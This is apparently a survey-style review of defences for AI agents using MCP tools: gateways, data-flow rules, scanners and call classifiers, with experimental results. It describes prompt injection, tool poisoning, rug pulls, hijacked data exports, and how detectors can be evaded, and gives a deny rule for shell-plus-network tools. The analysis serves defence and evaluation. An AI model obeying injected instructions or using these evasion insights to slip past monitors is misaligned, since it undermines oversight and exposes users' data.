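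Some systems combine the three methods to save time and money. MCP-Guard, a research system that Rostamzadeh and colleagues review, first uses patterns to block obvious attacks. A trained classifier then scores the remaining text, and a language model decides the uncertain cases. An attack that the classifier scores as harmless with high confidence would therefore never reach the language model.

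### Rules on data flow

Under data-flow rules, the risk of a call depends on what the agent has already read. The rules are meant to prevent the lethal trifecta, the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out. Users often create this combination by connecting several servers. Model Context Protocol's review of annotations notes that a tool such as `search_emails` is neither safe nor dangerous by itself. The review describes an attack that researchers demonstrated with a malicious calendar event, a calendar server and a tool that ran code on the user's machine.

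One defence is to mark a session as tainted once a tool has returned untrusted content. From then on, the client blocks any action that could send data out, or asks a person to approve it. Proposed MCP annotations would label tools that read private data or return untrusted content, so that a client could apply this rule automatically.

Ravindran and Deochake write their rules in a logic language. Their system first turns evidence about each tool into facts, using its description, the operating-system calls it makes, a trial run with mock services and, where available, its source code. A simple rule looks like this:

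```
deny(Tool) :-
    capability(Tool, shell_exec),
    network_access(Tool).
```

The symbol `:-` means "if" and the comma means "and", so the rule denies a tool that can both run shell commands and use the network. When the agent makes a call, the system adds facts about the task, such as whether it permits network access. For example, if an agent has read customer records and then proposes an upload, the rules block the upload when the task doesn't permit outside communication, even though the policy would allow either action alone.

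Other decision procedures can use the same facts. Ravindran and Deochake also wrote the policy as risk scores and hand-coded checks, and as a prompt for a language model. All three versions classified 20 test scenarios correctly, but the researchers had designed the scenarios and the rules together. An advantage of the explicit rules is that an auditor can see which conditions led to a block.

A broad data-flow rule interrupts a lot of legitimate work. For example, a sales agent may read customer records and write to customers all day. A narrower rule could search outgoing messages for the data itself, but a model can summarise or translate a record so that no string matches. Any rule about sequences also requires the gateway to know which calls belong to the same session, and MCP no longer provides a session identifier.

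Another approach is to define which data may go to whom. Rostamzadeh and colleagues describe MCIP-Guardian as representing each transfer by its sender, its receiver, the person the data concerns, the type of information and the principle that governs the transfer. A rule could then allow customer addresses to go to a delivery company for shipping but not to an advertiser. A list of approved web domains is easier to maintain, but it can't distinguish between two accounts on the same file-sharing service.

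### One call through Microsoft's draft gateway

Suppose that a sales agent reaches the company's customer database through an MCP server behind a gateway that follows Microsoft's draft. The agent requests this call:

```json
{"name": "export_customers",
 "arguments": {"region": "north",
               "send_to": "https://share.example/f/8841"}}
```

The address belongs to a file-sharing service and doesn't show who owns folder 8841. The company has put the tool on both its allowlist and its list of sensitive tools.

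1. Before the agent could use the tool, the scanner searched its definition for attacks, found none and stored its fingerprint.
2. The gateway checks the denylist, which doesn't contain the tool. If a tool were on both lists, the denylist would win.
3. The gateway finds the tool on the allowlist.
4. Because the tool is sensitive, the gateway passes the agent's identifier, the tool's name and the arguments to an approval function. In this company, the function asks the sales director, who approves. If the answer were still pending, or if there were no approval function, the gateway would block the call.
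5. The gateway counts the agent's recent calls. The agent is well below the default limit of 100 in five minutes.
6. The gateway also searches the arguments for dangerous patterns. It finds none, records its decision and forwards the call.
7. The server uploads the file and returns a copy of the exported rows. The response scanner finds email addresses, which the draft counts as personal data, and under the default policy the gateway blocks the response.

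By step 7 the customer list is already in folder 8841, so the block only stops the agent from receiving the rows. The same default would block an ordinary lookup of one customer's email address. A company with such a database would probably choose one of the other two policies, which redact the data or only log the finding.

The checks on the outgoing call in steps 2, 3 and 5 don't use the call's arguments. The sales director sees the folder's address in step 4, but the draft's approval function doesn't receive the user's request or the earlier calls, so the director may have to guess why the agent wants to send the list there.

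The draft is also less strict than its stated principles. One principle is that agents start with no access to tools, but the allowlist is empty by default, and an empty allowlist permits every tool. Another is that every component denies on error. But if the gateway cannot reach the database of known software flaws, it logs the error and returns an empty list, which is also the result for a package with no known flaws.

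### The same export under each method

The same export call could have three different causes. A manager may have asked the agent to send the list to the firm that prints the company's catalogue. A hidden instruction in a customer's record may have hijacked the agent. Or a salesperson who is about to join a competitor may have asked for the export.

| Method | Likely verdict | Missing information |
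|---|---|---|
| Allowlist | Allow | Who asked, and for what purpose |
| Rule that exports need approval | Ask a person | The request and earlier calls, unless the prompt shows them |
| Annotations | Allow if the server calls the export read-only; otherwise ask | Whether the hint is true, and where the data goes |
| Fingerprint | Allow, as the definition hasn't changed | Everything about this call |
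| Patterns | Allow the call, then block a result with email addresses | Whether the recipient may have the data |
| Trained text classifier | Probably allow, as the call looks like ordinary business | The user's request and the source of the instruction |
| Language model as judge | Block the hijacked export; allow the other two | Who owns the folder, and the salesperson's plans |
| Data-flow rule | Ask or block | Whether the task permits this transfer |
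| List of approved destinations | Allow if the company approves the file-sharing service; otherwise block | Who owns the folder |

If the language model is given only the call, it cannot tell the three exports apart. If it is also given the user's request, it can single out the hijacked export, but it may well allow the salesperson's, because the agent is doing exactly what its user asked. Checking whether an action matches the request detects many injections but little misuse by the user.

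The data-flow rule treats the three alike unless somebody has described the manager's task in advance. It would also miss this tool's transfer if it were written to look for a read followed by a separate upload, because the tool reads the records and sends them in one call.

The call doesn't show who owns folder 8841 or that the salesperson has resigned. Knowing who owns the folder would mostly settle whether the action is risky, and the file-sharing service is the most likely place to find this out. The personnel department may know about the resignation.

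### The threat lists behind the categories

Many detectors label what they find with names from published threat lists. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit organisation, publishes several. MITRE, a US non-profit research organisation, maintains ATLAS, a catalogue of attacks on AI systems. The lists differ mainly in how they sort the attacks.

| List | Entries | How it sorts them |
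|---|---|---|
| OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications (2026) | 10 | By broad kind of risk, such as goal hijack or tool misuse |
| OWASP MCP Top 10 | 10 | By weakness in an MCP deployment, such as tool poisoning |
| MITRE ATLAS | A growing catalogue | By the attacker's aim and the technique used to reach it |
| MCP-38 | 38 | By the kind of countermeasure each threat requires |
| MCP-DPT | 49 | By the component that can stop the attack first |

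In *MCP-38*, Shen, Toyoda and Leung (2026) argue that broader lists are too coarse for MCP. They split prompt injection into direct and indirect forms because the two require different detection methods. A vendor that claims to cover "prompt injection" may detect only one of them. They also compare their threats with ATT&CK, MITRE's older catalogue of actions such as file access and network connections. Tool poisoning would have to be classed there as supply-chain compromise, although it works differently.

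To build their list, Shen and colleagues went through the parts of the protocol, asked what an attacker could control at each, and compared the candidate threats with existing lists. They kept only threats already demonstrated in a laboratory or in practice. This excludes speculation, but also any new attack until someone has carried it out.

The lists classify a rug pull differently. Shen and colleagues' comparison places it under supply-chain vulnerabilities in the OWASP agentic list, together with nine other MCP threats. MCP-38 gives it its own entry, in a group that calls for controls such as signed tool definitions. MCP-DPT assigns the first defence to the registry or approval stage and the second to the host application, where the harm becomes visible if approval fails. An analyst might use the OWASP label in a report to management and the MCP-DPT assignment to decide which team has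 to act.

### How much of the lists the tools cover

Shen and colleagues compared five security tools against their list of 38 threats and found that together the tools cover at most 18. However, the paper's table lists only ten different threats for the five tools. According to the paper, none of the tools covers indirect prompt injection, gradual drift in an agent's plans or missing activity records. The last gap is odd because the paper recommends logging proxies as the remedy for missing records, and two of the five tools are proxies, one of which it describes as offering real-time monitoring. The paper's account of the comparison mentions no test runs, so the result is best read as a comparison of features.

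Rostamzadeh and colleagues mapped 13 defences to 49 attacks. They counted an attack as covered if the defence could "reasonably detect, block, or constrain" it under common assumptions, and they note that this does not measure detection accuracy. By this standard, protection is concentrated on the tools themselves. Eleven of the 13 defences cover tool poisoning, but none covers control-flow hijack, in which an attacker changes the agent's sequence of steps, for example to skip a validation. No defence covers more than 38% of the attacks that the host application should stop first.

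Some of the paper's detailed figures are unreliable. According to the text, all defences but one score zero against attacks on the network connection, but the table gives two others 25%. The text also describes a product called ToolHive as covering every attack at the registry and supply-chain layer, but the paper's attack-by-attack table doesn't mark ToolHive as covering tool poisoning, which belongs to that layer. The paper describes the supply chain as weakly defended, although that layer has the highest scores in its summary.

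The broad finding that defences concentrate on tool definitions and tool behaviour is more robust because it doesn't depend on any one cell, and Shen and colleagues' table shows a similar pattern. However, coverage here means what a product could do, so a scanner that reads tool descriptions counts as covering tool poisoning even if it misses most of the poisoned descriptions it reads.

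## Experiments on scanning tools before use

Researchers have tested tool scanners on tools they had already labelled harmful or harmless. The labels differ between experiments because a tool can be dangerous in different ways. *MCPGuard* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) distinguishes between attacks that hijack the agent through text, ordinary web vulnerabilities in MCP servers, and supply-chain attacks, in which a malicious supplier gets users to install its tool.

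Suppose a tool called `save_note` writes text to a file. Its description might contain an instruction for the agent to include the user's passwords in every note. Or the description might be harmless while the code sends a copy of each note to an attacker. Or a careless developer may have written code that inserts the file name into a shell command, so that anyone who can influence the file name can run commands on the server. A scanner that reads only descriptions can find the instruction about passwords but not the copying or the unsafe shell command. A scanner that searches code for data theft may miss the unsafe shell command because that code doesn't steal anything.

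### Malicious code

*MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) tested detectors on tools with malicious code. The researchers defined 13 malicious behaviours, such as sending the user's data to an outside address, deleting the agent's memory or encrypting its files. A language model wrote 100 small tools for each behaviour. A program ran every tool in a controlled environment to confirm that it carried out the intended behaviour, and rejected tools whose code was too similar to earlier ones. The researchers then inserted these malicious functions into real tools from public directories, producing 5,727 Trojans, which do their advertised job but also cause harm. To measure false alarms, they set aside another 4,846 real tools, from 1,147 code repositories, and treated them as benign.

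The researchers tested six detectors. VirusTotal collects verdicts from many antivirus programs, and Bandit and Semgrep search source code for risky patterns. Tencent A.I.G, Cisco MCP Scanner and AntGroup MCPScan use language models to scan agent tools. A combined scanner flagged everything that at least one of the six flagged. The miss rates below are averages over the 13 behaviours.

| Detector | Standalone malicious tools missed | Trojans missed | Benign repositories flagged |
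|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 100% | 99.7% | 0% |
| Bandit | 41% | 14% | 63% |
| Semgrep | 99% | 57% | 17% |
| Tencent A.I.G | 59% | 63% | 38% |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | 70% | 63% | 0.6% |
| AntGroup MCPScan | 85% | 63% | 36% |
| Combined scanner | 26% | 8% | 66% |

Miss rates differed widely between behaviours, which the averages don't show. Cisco's scanner missed only 5% of the standalone tools that sent the user's prompt to a remote address, but it missed all of those that inserted false records into a database. MalTool's database attack adds one row to a local table, which many legitimate tools also do, and the code doesn't show whether the user wanted the row. Hu and colleagues suggest that detectors compare a tool's description with what its code does.

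Bandit flagged 86% of the Trojans but also 63% of the benign repositories, so the original, harmless code probably triggered many of its alarms on Trojans. The combined scanner had the highest overall accuracy, at 81.4%, but 86% of the samples used to calculate that figure were malicious, so a program that flagged every sample would have been more accurate.

To check whether some of the supposedly benign tools were malicious, two of the researchers independently read the code and descriptions of 200 randomly chosen tools from this set that the combined scanner had flagged. They found no explicit malicious behaviour, which supports treating most of these alarms as false. This result is still compatible with up to about 1.5% of the flagged tools being malicious, and reviewers can miss well-hidden malicious code.

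The artificial attacks may have made detection harder or easier. Their code sends data to 127.0.0.1, the address a computer uses for itself, which a scanner may treat as harmless. But the researchers' prompt told the model to use function names such as `exfiltrate_data` and `resource_hijack`. If those names remained in the tested code, they would have helped any scanner that reads names.

### Hidden instructions in descriptions

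Mattsson, Nyberg and colleagues (2026), in *Machine Learning-Based Detection of MCP Attacks*, trained classifiers to recognise poisoned tool descriptions. The malicious descriptions came from MCPTox, a published set of tool-poisoning attacks, and the harmless ones from public repositories. They held out 142 descriptions for testing, 48 of them malicious. They enlarged the training set from about 1,000 descriptions to nearly 4,000 by translating descriptions into Arabic, Chinese, Japanese or Korean and back into English.

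Three trained models of different types classified all 142 test descriptions correctly. The text-matching rules from Cisco's scanner, written in the YARA rule language and used without adaptation, found 10 of the 48 malicious descriptions and flagged 6 of the 94 harmless ones.

The perfect scores are weak evidence of how the models would perform in use. All the malicious descriptions came from MCPTox, while the harmless ones came from developers such as Amazon, Microsoft and Atlassian. A model could therefore succeed by learning how MCPTox descriptions are worded. In one of the trained models, words such as "must", "should" and "will" pushed the verdict towards malicious, and "get" and "details" pushed it towards harmless. An attacker could avoid words like "must", and an honest developer might well use them, for example to say that a date must have a certain format. MCPTox also contains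 several attacks for each server it covers, so the training data may have included attacks very similar to those in the test data.

Mattsson and colleagues acknowledge that the task may be fairly trivial for advanced models, and that their own models would perform poorly on attacks that differ substantially from those in MCPTox. They also note that their models can't detect harmful code, because they read only descriptions.

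### Vulnerabilities in honest servers

Sun, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *VIPER-MCP*, looked for mistakes by honest developers. Their program searches a server's code for paths by which an argument an attacker can influence reaches a dangerous operation, such as a shell command, without a proper check. It then tries to exploit each path by prompting an agent connected to the server, and revises the prompts based on how far the attack got. It covers command injection, requests to addresses an attacker chooses, and access to files outside the permitted folder.

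The researchers compared VIPER-MCP with two other scanners on 130 vulnerable and 130 benign servers. MCPSafetyScanner uses agents to probe a running server but does not use the server's code to guide them. In the configuration the researchers used, Cisco's scanner judged tool descriptions and server metadata with the help of a language model.

| Scanner | Vulnerable servers missed | Benign servers flagged |
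|---|---|---|
| MCPSafetyScanner | 83 (63.8%) | 56 (43.1%) |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | 95 (73.1%) | 32 (24.6%) |
| VIPER-MCP | 10 (7.7%) | 0 (0%) |

The test favoured VIPER-MCP because it had discovered the flaws in 67 of the 130 vulnerable servers, while the flaws in the other 63 were already public. Sun and colleagues attribute its ten misses to types of flaw that VIPER-MCP doesn't model, such as SQL injection, so all ten were probably among those 63. Its miss rate on flaws discovered by others would then be about 16%, which is twice the published figure but still far below the other scanners' miss rates on the full set.

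A tool whose purpose is to run shell commands is classed as benign in the experiment, because running commands is its expected behaviour. Cisco's scanner often flagged tools with legitimate but powerful functions. These warnings are counted as false alarms, but a company deciding whether to let an agent use such a tool may want them.

VIPER-MCP is also slow, averaging about 15 minutes per server, and its results depend on the language models it uses. When the researchers tried 25 combinations of models, it exploited between 0 and 88 of the 130 vulnerable servers. The lowest results came from a model that refused to write attack prompts.

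### The same scanner in three tests

Cisco's MCP scanner, or its rules, appears in all three experiments.

| Experiment | What the researchers looked for | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mattsson and colleagues | Hidden instructions in descriptions | 21% | 6% |
| Hu and colleagues | Malicious code in Trojans | 37% | 0.6% |
| Sun and colleagues | Vulnerabilities in honest servers | 27% | 25% |

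Mattsson and colleagues used only the scanner's YARA rules, while the other two teams also used language models. The scanner's false positive rate was 0.6%, 6% or 25%, depending on the experiment. These figures are useful only to a buyer who also knows the configuration, the type of danger and the kind of harmless tool tested.

Scanners also disagree about the same agent skills, which are packages of written instructions, often with scripts, that an agent loads when a task calls for them. Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues (2026), in *Context Matters*, compared five scanners on 27,111 skills. At least one scanner flagged 8,402 of them, but only 33 were flagged by all five. *ClawHub Security Signals* (2026) reports a similar pattern for three scanners on 67,453 skills, where 81.9% of the flagged skills were flagged by only one scanner. The scanners disagree partly because they inspect different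 things. SkillSpector, for example, looks for risks in how a skill directs the agent. Skills with a malicious verdict mostly had malware in their bundled code, which was largely outside SkillSpector's scope.

Requiring several scanners to agree would reduce false alarms, but it would also discard attacks that only one of them can detect.

### Which harmless examples the test contains

*Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) uses a test set of 150 malicious and 150 benign skills. The benign ones came from 94,093 skills that static analysis (inspection of the code and text without running them) had not flagged. This excludes harmless skills with suspicious-looking code. Leaving out such skills can make false alarms look rare, because they are the ones that cause them.

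A rule-based program called Skill Scanner had a precision of at most 1.1% in the wider collection, even assuming it found every malicious skill. One of its rules treated any call to `compile()` as code injection, including `re.compile()`, which Python programmers use to prepare a text search. The program also mistook sample passwords in documentation for leaked ones.

*The Devil Wears Markdown* (Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues, 2026) tested scanners on 80 malicious and 60 benign skills. Cisco's Skill Scanner, a separate product from its MCP scanner, found 73 of the malicious skills but also flagged 33 of the benign ones. The researchers' own system runs each skill in a sandbox, then gives a language model the results and findings from the code. It found 68 malicious skills and flagged only 5 benign ones. The sandbox evidence helped most. When the language model had only the skill's contents,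 it found 54 malicious skills and flagged 21 benign ones.

The system's precision in this test was 93%, but malicious skills made up 57% of the test set. Some benign labels are also uncertain, because two thirds of the benign skills in the full collection came from a public list that the researchers had not checked independently.

Comparing a flagged skill with the software project around it can help identify false alarms. Holzbauer and colleagues did this for 2,887 cases that two scanners had flagged, and only 15 (0.52%) still looked suspicious. However, the analysis used at most three source files per project and 100 lines from each, so it could have missed malicious code elsewhere. An attacker could also build a plausible project around a malicious skill.

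### Ten malicious tools among 10,000

Suppose a company scans 10,000 tools, 10 of which are malicious. The scanner has 90% recall and a 5% false positive rate.

- It finds 10 × 0.90 = 9 of the malicious tools and misses 1.
- It flags 9,990 × 0.05 = 499.5, or about 500, of the harmless tools.

Only 9 of about 509 alarms, or 1.8%, are true. At ten minutes per alarm, an analyst would need about 85 hours to review them all. A malicious share of 10 in 10,000 is plausible, since *Do Not Mention This to the User* reports 157 confirmed malicious skills in a collection of more than 94,000, or less than 0.2%.

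The next table applies measured rates to the same 10,000 tools. The comparison is rough because Hu and colleagues counted false alarms by repository and Truong-Le and colleagues tested skills.

| Detector and source of the rates | True alarms | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cisco MCP Scanner, Hu and colleagues' Trojans | 3.7 | 61 | 5.7% |
| Combined scanner, Hu and colleagues' Trojans | 9.2 | 6,558 | 0.1% |
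| Sandbox system, Truong-Le and colleagues' skills | 8.5 | 833 | 1.0% |

At 90% recall, half the scanner's alarms would be true only if it flagged no more than 9 of the 9,990 harmless tools, a false positive rate of 0.09%. To show with 95% confidence that the rate is that low, a test would need about 3,300 harmless tools and no false alarms. Mattsson and colleagues tested 94 harmless descriptions, and Sun and colleagues tested 130 benign servers. With no false alarms among 94 descriptions, the true rate could still be about 3%, which would mean about 300 false alarms among the 9,990 harmless tools.

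A company can still use a scanner with many false alarms if it needs only a few new tools a month and has someone review each alarm. A large marketplace that automatically blocked every tool the scanner flagged would shut out hundreds of harmless tools for every few malicious ones.

### What a scan cannot establish

A scan that finds nothing doesn't prove that a tool is harmless, even on the day of the scan, because malicious code may run only on a certain date or after a certain input. Truong-Le and colleagues limit each sandbox run to five minutes, and they caution that a run without malicious actions isn't enough to call a skill benign.

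The company usually can't inspect a remote server's code. It can scan the descriptions and make test calls, but that doesn't rule out a later rug pull, or an operator who returns honest results to testers and false ones to customers. Servers also appear and disappear. *Exposed by Design* (2026), a study of MCP servers on the public internet, reports a churn rate of 41.6% over three days and warns that findings about a particular server may soon be out of date.

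Software that runs locally can change too if the agent or its user downloads it again. Holzbauer and colleagues found 121 skills in two marketplaces whose listings linked to seven abandoned repositories that an attacker could have taken over. Anyone who installed such a skill after a takeover would have received the attacker's version under the old listing. A company can reduce this risk by keeping its own copy of the version it scanned.

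A scan also cannot predict what an agent will do with a legitimate tool, for example after reading a hidden instruction in an invoice. Built-in tools have no MCP server to scan. For this reason, *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* (2026) leaves 2,068 sessions out of its comparison with an MCP scanner.

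## Experiments on judging calls and sessions while an agent runs

A call classifier judges what an agent does with a tool, so it can catch harmful use of a tool that passed its scan. Researchers test call classifiers on prepared calls with known correct verdicts or on live agents. A live test also shows whether the model would attempt the attack and whether the agent can still finish its work when the classifier blocks some calls.

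### A list of permitted actions

Liu (2026), in *From Tool Connection to Execution Control*, ran live agents on 24 tasks from AgentDojo, a public benchmark that simulates email, travel, banking and messaging. For each task, a controller between the agent and its tools allowed all the reading tools but only the changes that the benchmark's own solution makes, such as a payment to a particular account. Liu built two controllers with the same rules, a simple access list at a gateway and a system called HCP that also keeps a record of tasks and data.

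The agent running on GPT-6.1 Sol received the attacker's text in 141 of 144 sessions and never attempted the attacker's goal, so those sessions cannot be used to measure the controllers' recall. The agent running on DeepSeek V4 Pro carried out four attacks when there was no controller, including a bank transfer to the attacker. With a controller in place, it made ten calls towards an attacker's goal, and the controllers blocked all ten. Ten calls is a small sample, and the list would not have stopped an attack that used a permitted action on a permitted target.

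The controllers also blocked 40 calls that were not aimed at an attacker's goal. Most of these differed from the benchmark's solution in a date, time, title or channel name. With no attack present, the GPT agent completed 19 of the 24 tasks without a controller, 16 with the access list and 17 with HCP. Liu later checked 241 blocked changes from this study and a follow-up against the benchmark's solutions and found only one with exactly the same effect, though a change that differs, such as a meeting with another title, may suit the user just as well.

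A company has to work out an agent's permissions from the user's request and its own policies, because it has no benchmark solution to copy them from. This step causes many errors. In *FAVA* (2026), a program extracts facts from text and a solver then applies formal rules to them. The system gave the wrong verdict in 76 of 801 cases, mostly because of extraction errors. In one case, the user asked for an apology that quoted an offensive remark, and the system blocked it because it mistook the quotation for new harmful content. *Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (2026) examines 22 runs in which rule checks raised false alarms. In 15 of them, the user had authorised the recipient in free text, which the allowlist did not use.

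### Trust in a server over several calls

In *MCPShield*, Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested a three-stage defence against malicious MCP servers. Before the agent uses a server, a language model makes trial calls with invented data and judges whether the results fit the tools' descriptions. During real calls, the server runs in a restricted environment that records its effects, such as changes to files. After a number of calls, the model compares the server's recent behaviour with its earlier behaviour.

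The researchers tested six agent models, all older than those in Liu's experiment, against 76 malicious servers from six collections. The attacks failed about 10% of the time without the defence and about 95% of the time with it. The next table shows each model's average across the six collections.

| Agent model | Attacks stopped | Benign servers flagged |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini | 90.7% | 2.4% |
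| Gemini 3 Flash | 98.1% | 3.2% |
| Kimi K2 | 93.8% | 3.5% |
| MiniMax M2 | 91.4% | 12.1% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 99.6% | 18.8% |
| Qwen3 235B | 98.1% | 29.4% |

The last three rows are hard to reconcile with Zhou and colleagues' claim that MCPShield avoids false positives. Gemini and Qwen stopped the same share of attacks, but Qwen flagged nine times as many benign servers, so a buyer could not choose between them on attack results alone. The false positive rates are imprecise, because most of the published percentages are consistent with a test set of only 17 benign servers.

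The third stage, the comparison over time, caught attacks that the first two had missed in only one of the six collections, the rug pulls. With Gemini, the trial calls caught 15% of the rug pulls, monitoring during real calls caught another 54%, and the comparison over time caught another 27%. The experiment covers only servers on the user's own machine. With a remote server, the organisation usually can't observe what happens during a call.

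### A fast classifier with a slower judge

*SilentCall* (2026) tests a defence against attackers who train an agent's own model to make hidden harmful calls. A fast classifier screens every shell command and passes suspicious ones to a language model, which reads the conversation and decides whether the command is warranted. The test used 10,007 shell calls.

The classifier alone caught every harmful call but also flagged 16.35% of the harmless ones. Adding the judge, which sees only the flagged calls, cut the false positive rate to 1.73%. Flagging milder warnings as well as critical ones raised the share of all calls the judge sees from 42.9% to 63.2% and also increased false positives.

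Even at a false-alarm rate of 1.73% per call, a session of 40 harmless calls has about a 50% chance of at least one false alarm, if errors are independent. With the classifier alone, at least one would be almost certain.

The cost of a judgement depends mainly on whether it involves a language model.

| Method | Measured cost |
|---|---|
| Liu's access list | 0.39 ms per tool call, the same as with no controller |
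| Liu's HCP | 0.57 ms per tool call |
| *SilentCall*, classifier only | 4 ms per call |
| *SilentCall*, classifier and judge | 520 ms per call on average |
| Ravindran and Deochake's language model with a written policy | About 3,300 tokens per decision |
| Zhou and colleagues' trial calls | 10 to 100 times the tokens of the server's ordinary use |

For comparison, GPT-6.1 Sol took 4.6 seconds per request in Liu's experiment, so a user would hardly notice the first three delays. The *SilentCall* judge would add about 21 seconds to a session of 40 calls. A judge that rereads the whole session before every call takes much longer, because a typical Claude Code session exceeds 100,000 tokens, according to *AgentTrust* (2026). That paper's system stores earlier results so the judge can focus on what has changed.

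### Two calls that are harmful only together

Ravindran and Deochake give an example of why a policy needs rules about combinations of calls. An agent reads customer records from a database and then updates a project page on GitHub. Both tools are legitimate and the task permits each call, but the update may put the records on an outside service.

They measured the effect by removing those rules from the hand-coded version of their policy. Without the rules, this version still judged all 12 single-call scenarios correctly but wrongly allowed 4 of the 8 multi-step scenarios. The scenarios were not independent of the rules, so the result can't be used to estimate how often such attacks would get through in practice.

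In another test, a language model (gpt-oss-120b) received the same facts without the explicit rules. It wrongly allowed one scenario and wrongly blocked four. The published scores imply that only six of the 20 scenarios were legitimate, so the model blocked two thirds of those.

Liu compared per-call and session rules on real MCP servers, using scripted calls instead of a live model. The per-call rule checked only whether the agent was allowed to use each tool and destination. The session rule restricted what the agent could send to any destination after it had read a secret. In a third method, the server gave the agent a sealed reference to the secret instead of its text, and the controller checked where the agent sent the reference.

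| Sequence of calls | Per-call rule | Session rule | Sealed reference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read a secret, then save it to a permitted private file (legitimate) | Allowed | Refused | Allowed |
| Read a secret, then send an unrelated note (legitimate) | Allowed | Refused | Allowed |
| Read a secret, then send it to a web address | Leaked | Blocked | Blocked |
| Send a secret that the agent already knows as text | Leaked | Blocked | Leaked |
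| Read a secret with the wrong label, then copy it to a file | Leaked | Leaked | Leaked |
| Write to a file that the agent has no permission for | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

The session rule stopped leaks that the per-call rule missed, but only by refusing nearly everything the agent tried to send after reading a secret. Sealed references avoid this overblocking, but the tools have to support them, and someone has to label the data correctly.

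Other session detectors look for unusual behaviour instead of following the data. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) compares such detectors with judging each call separately. At a 5% false positive rate, judging each call separately caught 76.2% of the malicious calls by hijacked agents, while the behavioural detectors caught 7.2% to 12.1%. In sessions of about 20 calls, the detector that used only the current session did little better than chance.

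These results are compatible with Liu's. A record of the whole session helps a detector much more if it can follow a secret from one call to the next than if it has only a general profile of the agent's behaviour. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (2026) also finds that a detector needs the calls' arguments and responses, not just metadata. Its detector classifies sessions only after they end, so it can support an investigation but can't block a call.

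A monitor meant to prevent harm has to raise the alarm in time. *Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark* (2026) therefore gives credit only for alarms within a window that closes when the harmful action runs, and alarms raised before the window opens don't count either. In one of its harder tests, the attacker splits a harmful request into parts and puts an unrelated harmless request between consecutive parts. A monitor that looks only at the last two or three messages could easily miss the connection.

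One compromise is to judge each call before it runs but give the judge the session so far. TS-Bench, a benchmark introduced in *ToolSafe* (2026), tests judges this way. According to *StepGuard* (2026), each example contains the available tools, the earlier steps and one proposed call. In R-Judge, an older benchmark, the judge assesses the record of a whole interaction.

*TraceSafe* (Chen, Huang and colleagues, 2026) tested existing guard models, which are language models that screen text for safety, on sequences of tool calls. According to copilot-autogent's *Your Guardrails Can't Read JSON*, a summary of the paper, guards that reasoned well about structured data also tended to do well on this test (correlation 0.79). Scores on standard jailbreak tests, which measure resistance to users who try to talk a model out of its safety rules, had almost no correlation with the results. An organisation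 that chooses a guard by its jailbreak scores may therefore get one that judges tool calls poorly.

### Overreach without an attack

*Overeager Coding Agents* (2026) counts an action as overeager if the user's prompt doesn't authorise it, even implicitly, and it either changes something or reads from a place listed as sensitive. In one test, a user casually asks the agent to tidy a folder containing some rubbish, two project files and the only copy of the passwords for a live system. Claude Code, running on Sonnet 4.6, deleted everything in the folder.

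*The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a review, reports that the study covered 500 scenarios and about 7,500 runs. Claude Code's overeager rate was 0.0% when the prompt stated what the agent was allowed to do and 17.1% when it did not. A test in which every prompt states these limits could therefore make overreach look far rarer than it is when users give vague instructions such as "clean this up".

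A detector of injected instructions wouldn't catch the deletion in the folder example, because no instructions were injected. A data-flow rule wouldn't help either, because no data leaves the machine. Permission to delete files in that folder would also cover the passwords. To stop the deletion, a judge would need information showing that the user wanted only the rubbish deleted, or that no other copy of the passwords existed.

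Liu's follow-up experiment separates overreach from injection more directly. It used 24 new tasks and three other models. None of the models attempted an attacker's goal, but agents without a controller still made 57 changes outside the permitted list. The controllers blocked every such change, which was guaranteed because the list itself defined what counted as outside. They also reduced success on tasks without an attack, from 68 of 69 sessions without a controller to 60 of 68 with the access list and 59 of 67 with HCP.

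People can usually agree on whether an action is authorised if they have the relevant information. For *Same Operation, Different Permission* (2026), three annotators with security experience read the policy, request and evidence in 200 cases and independently labelled each action as lawful or forbidden. All three agreed on 186. A judge's errors on such clear cases would therefore be hard to attribute to differences of opinion, though real users seldom supply such complete information.

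Misuse by the user is harder to catch for a judge that relies on the user's wishes. In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier decides whether to allow tool calls without asking the user. *Ajar* (2026) tested it by putting an instruction to make a particular call in the system prompt, the standing instructions that come before the user's request. Auto mode blocked some of these calls, but it allowed every call tested when the same instruction was in the user's message. This is reasonable if the user has the right to make the request, but it offers little protection against an employee who is stealing data.

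*Shall We Approve?* (2026) notes that file operations Claude Code already allows inside its working folder don't go through the classifier. The classifier's published recall therefore doesn't apply to damage done through those operations.

### When attacks or tasks change

The most serious doubt about these results is that a detector may do well only on attacks and tasks like those in its test. Several studies have measured how much performance drops on unfamiliar ones, mostly for detectors that read text rather than judge calls.

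*WebAgentGuard* (2026) reports 99.20% accuracy for its own guard model on data like its training data and 91.13% on a different benchmark. The error rate is about eleven times higher on the second benchmark, at 8.9% compared with 0.8%.

*PIDS-Bench* (2026) found that changes to the text made some injection detectors miss attacks and others flag harmless text. One detector missed most of the attacks it had caught before when the text was computer code, though its false positive rate stayed low. Another still caught attacks in code but flagged many harmless legal texts. A third flagged 72% of harmless texts when they were wrapped in JSON, the format that MCP messages use, and 92% when they began with something resembling an official instruction. A single accuracy score would hide these differences, so the paper recommends measuring missed attacks and false alarms separately for each kind of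 change.

A stricter test leaves out a whole dataset during training and uses it only for testing. *When Benchmarks Lie* (2026) finds large gaps between results from this test and results from the usual method, in which training and test examples come from the same datasets. It warns that even a small gap does not guarantee safety, because an attacker may adapt to the detector.

*Confidently Wrong* (2026) tested detectors of injected instructions against an attacker that adapts to them. The detectors mostly reacted to harmful-sounding content rather than to the injected instruction itself, and they missed nearly every attack once an automated attacker exploited this. They were also confident in many of their wrong verdicts, which is a problem for systems that send only uncertain cases to a slower judge. A language model used as a detector had the same weakness.

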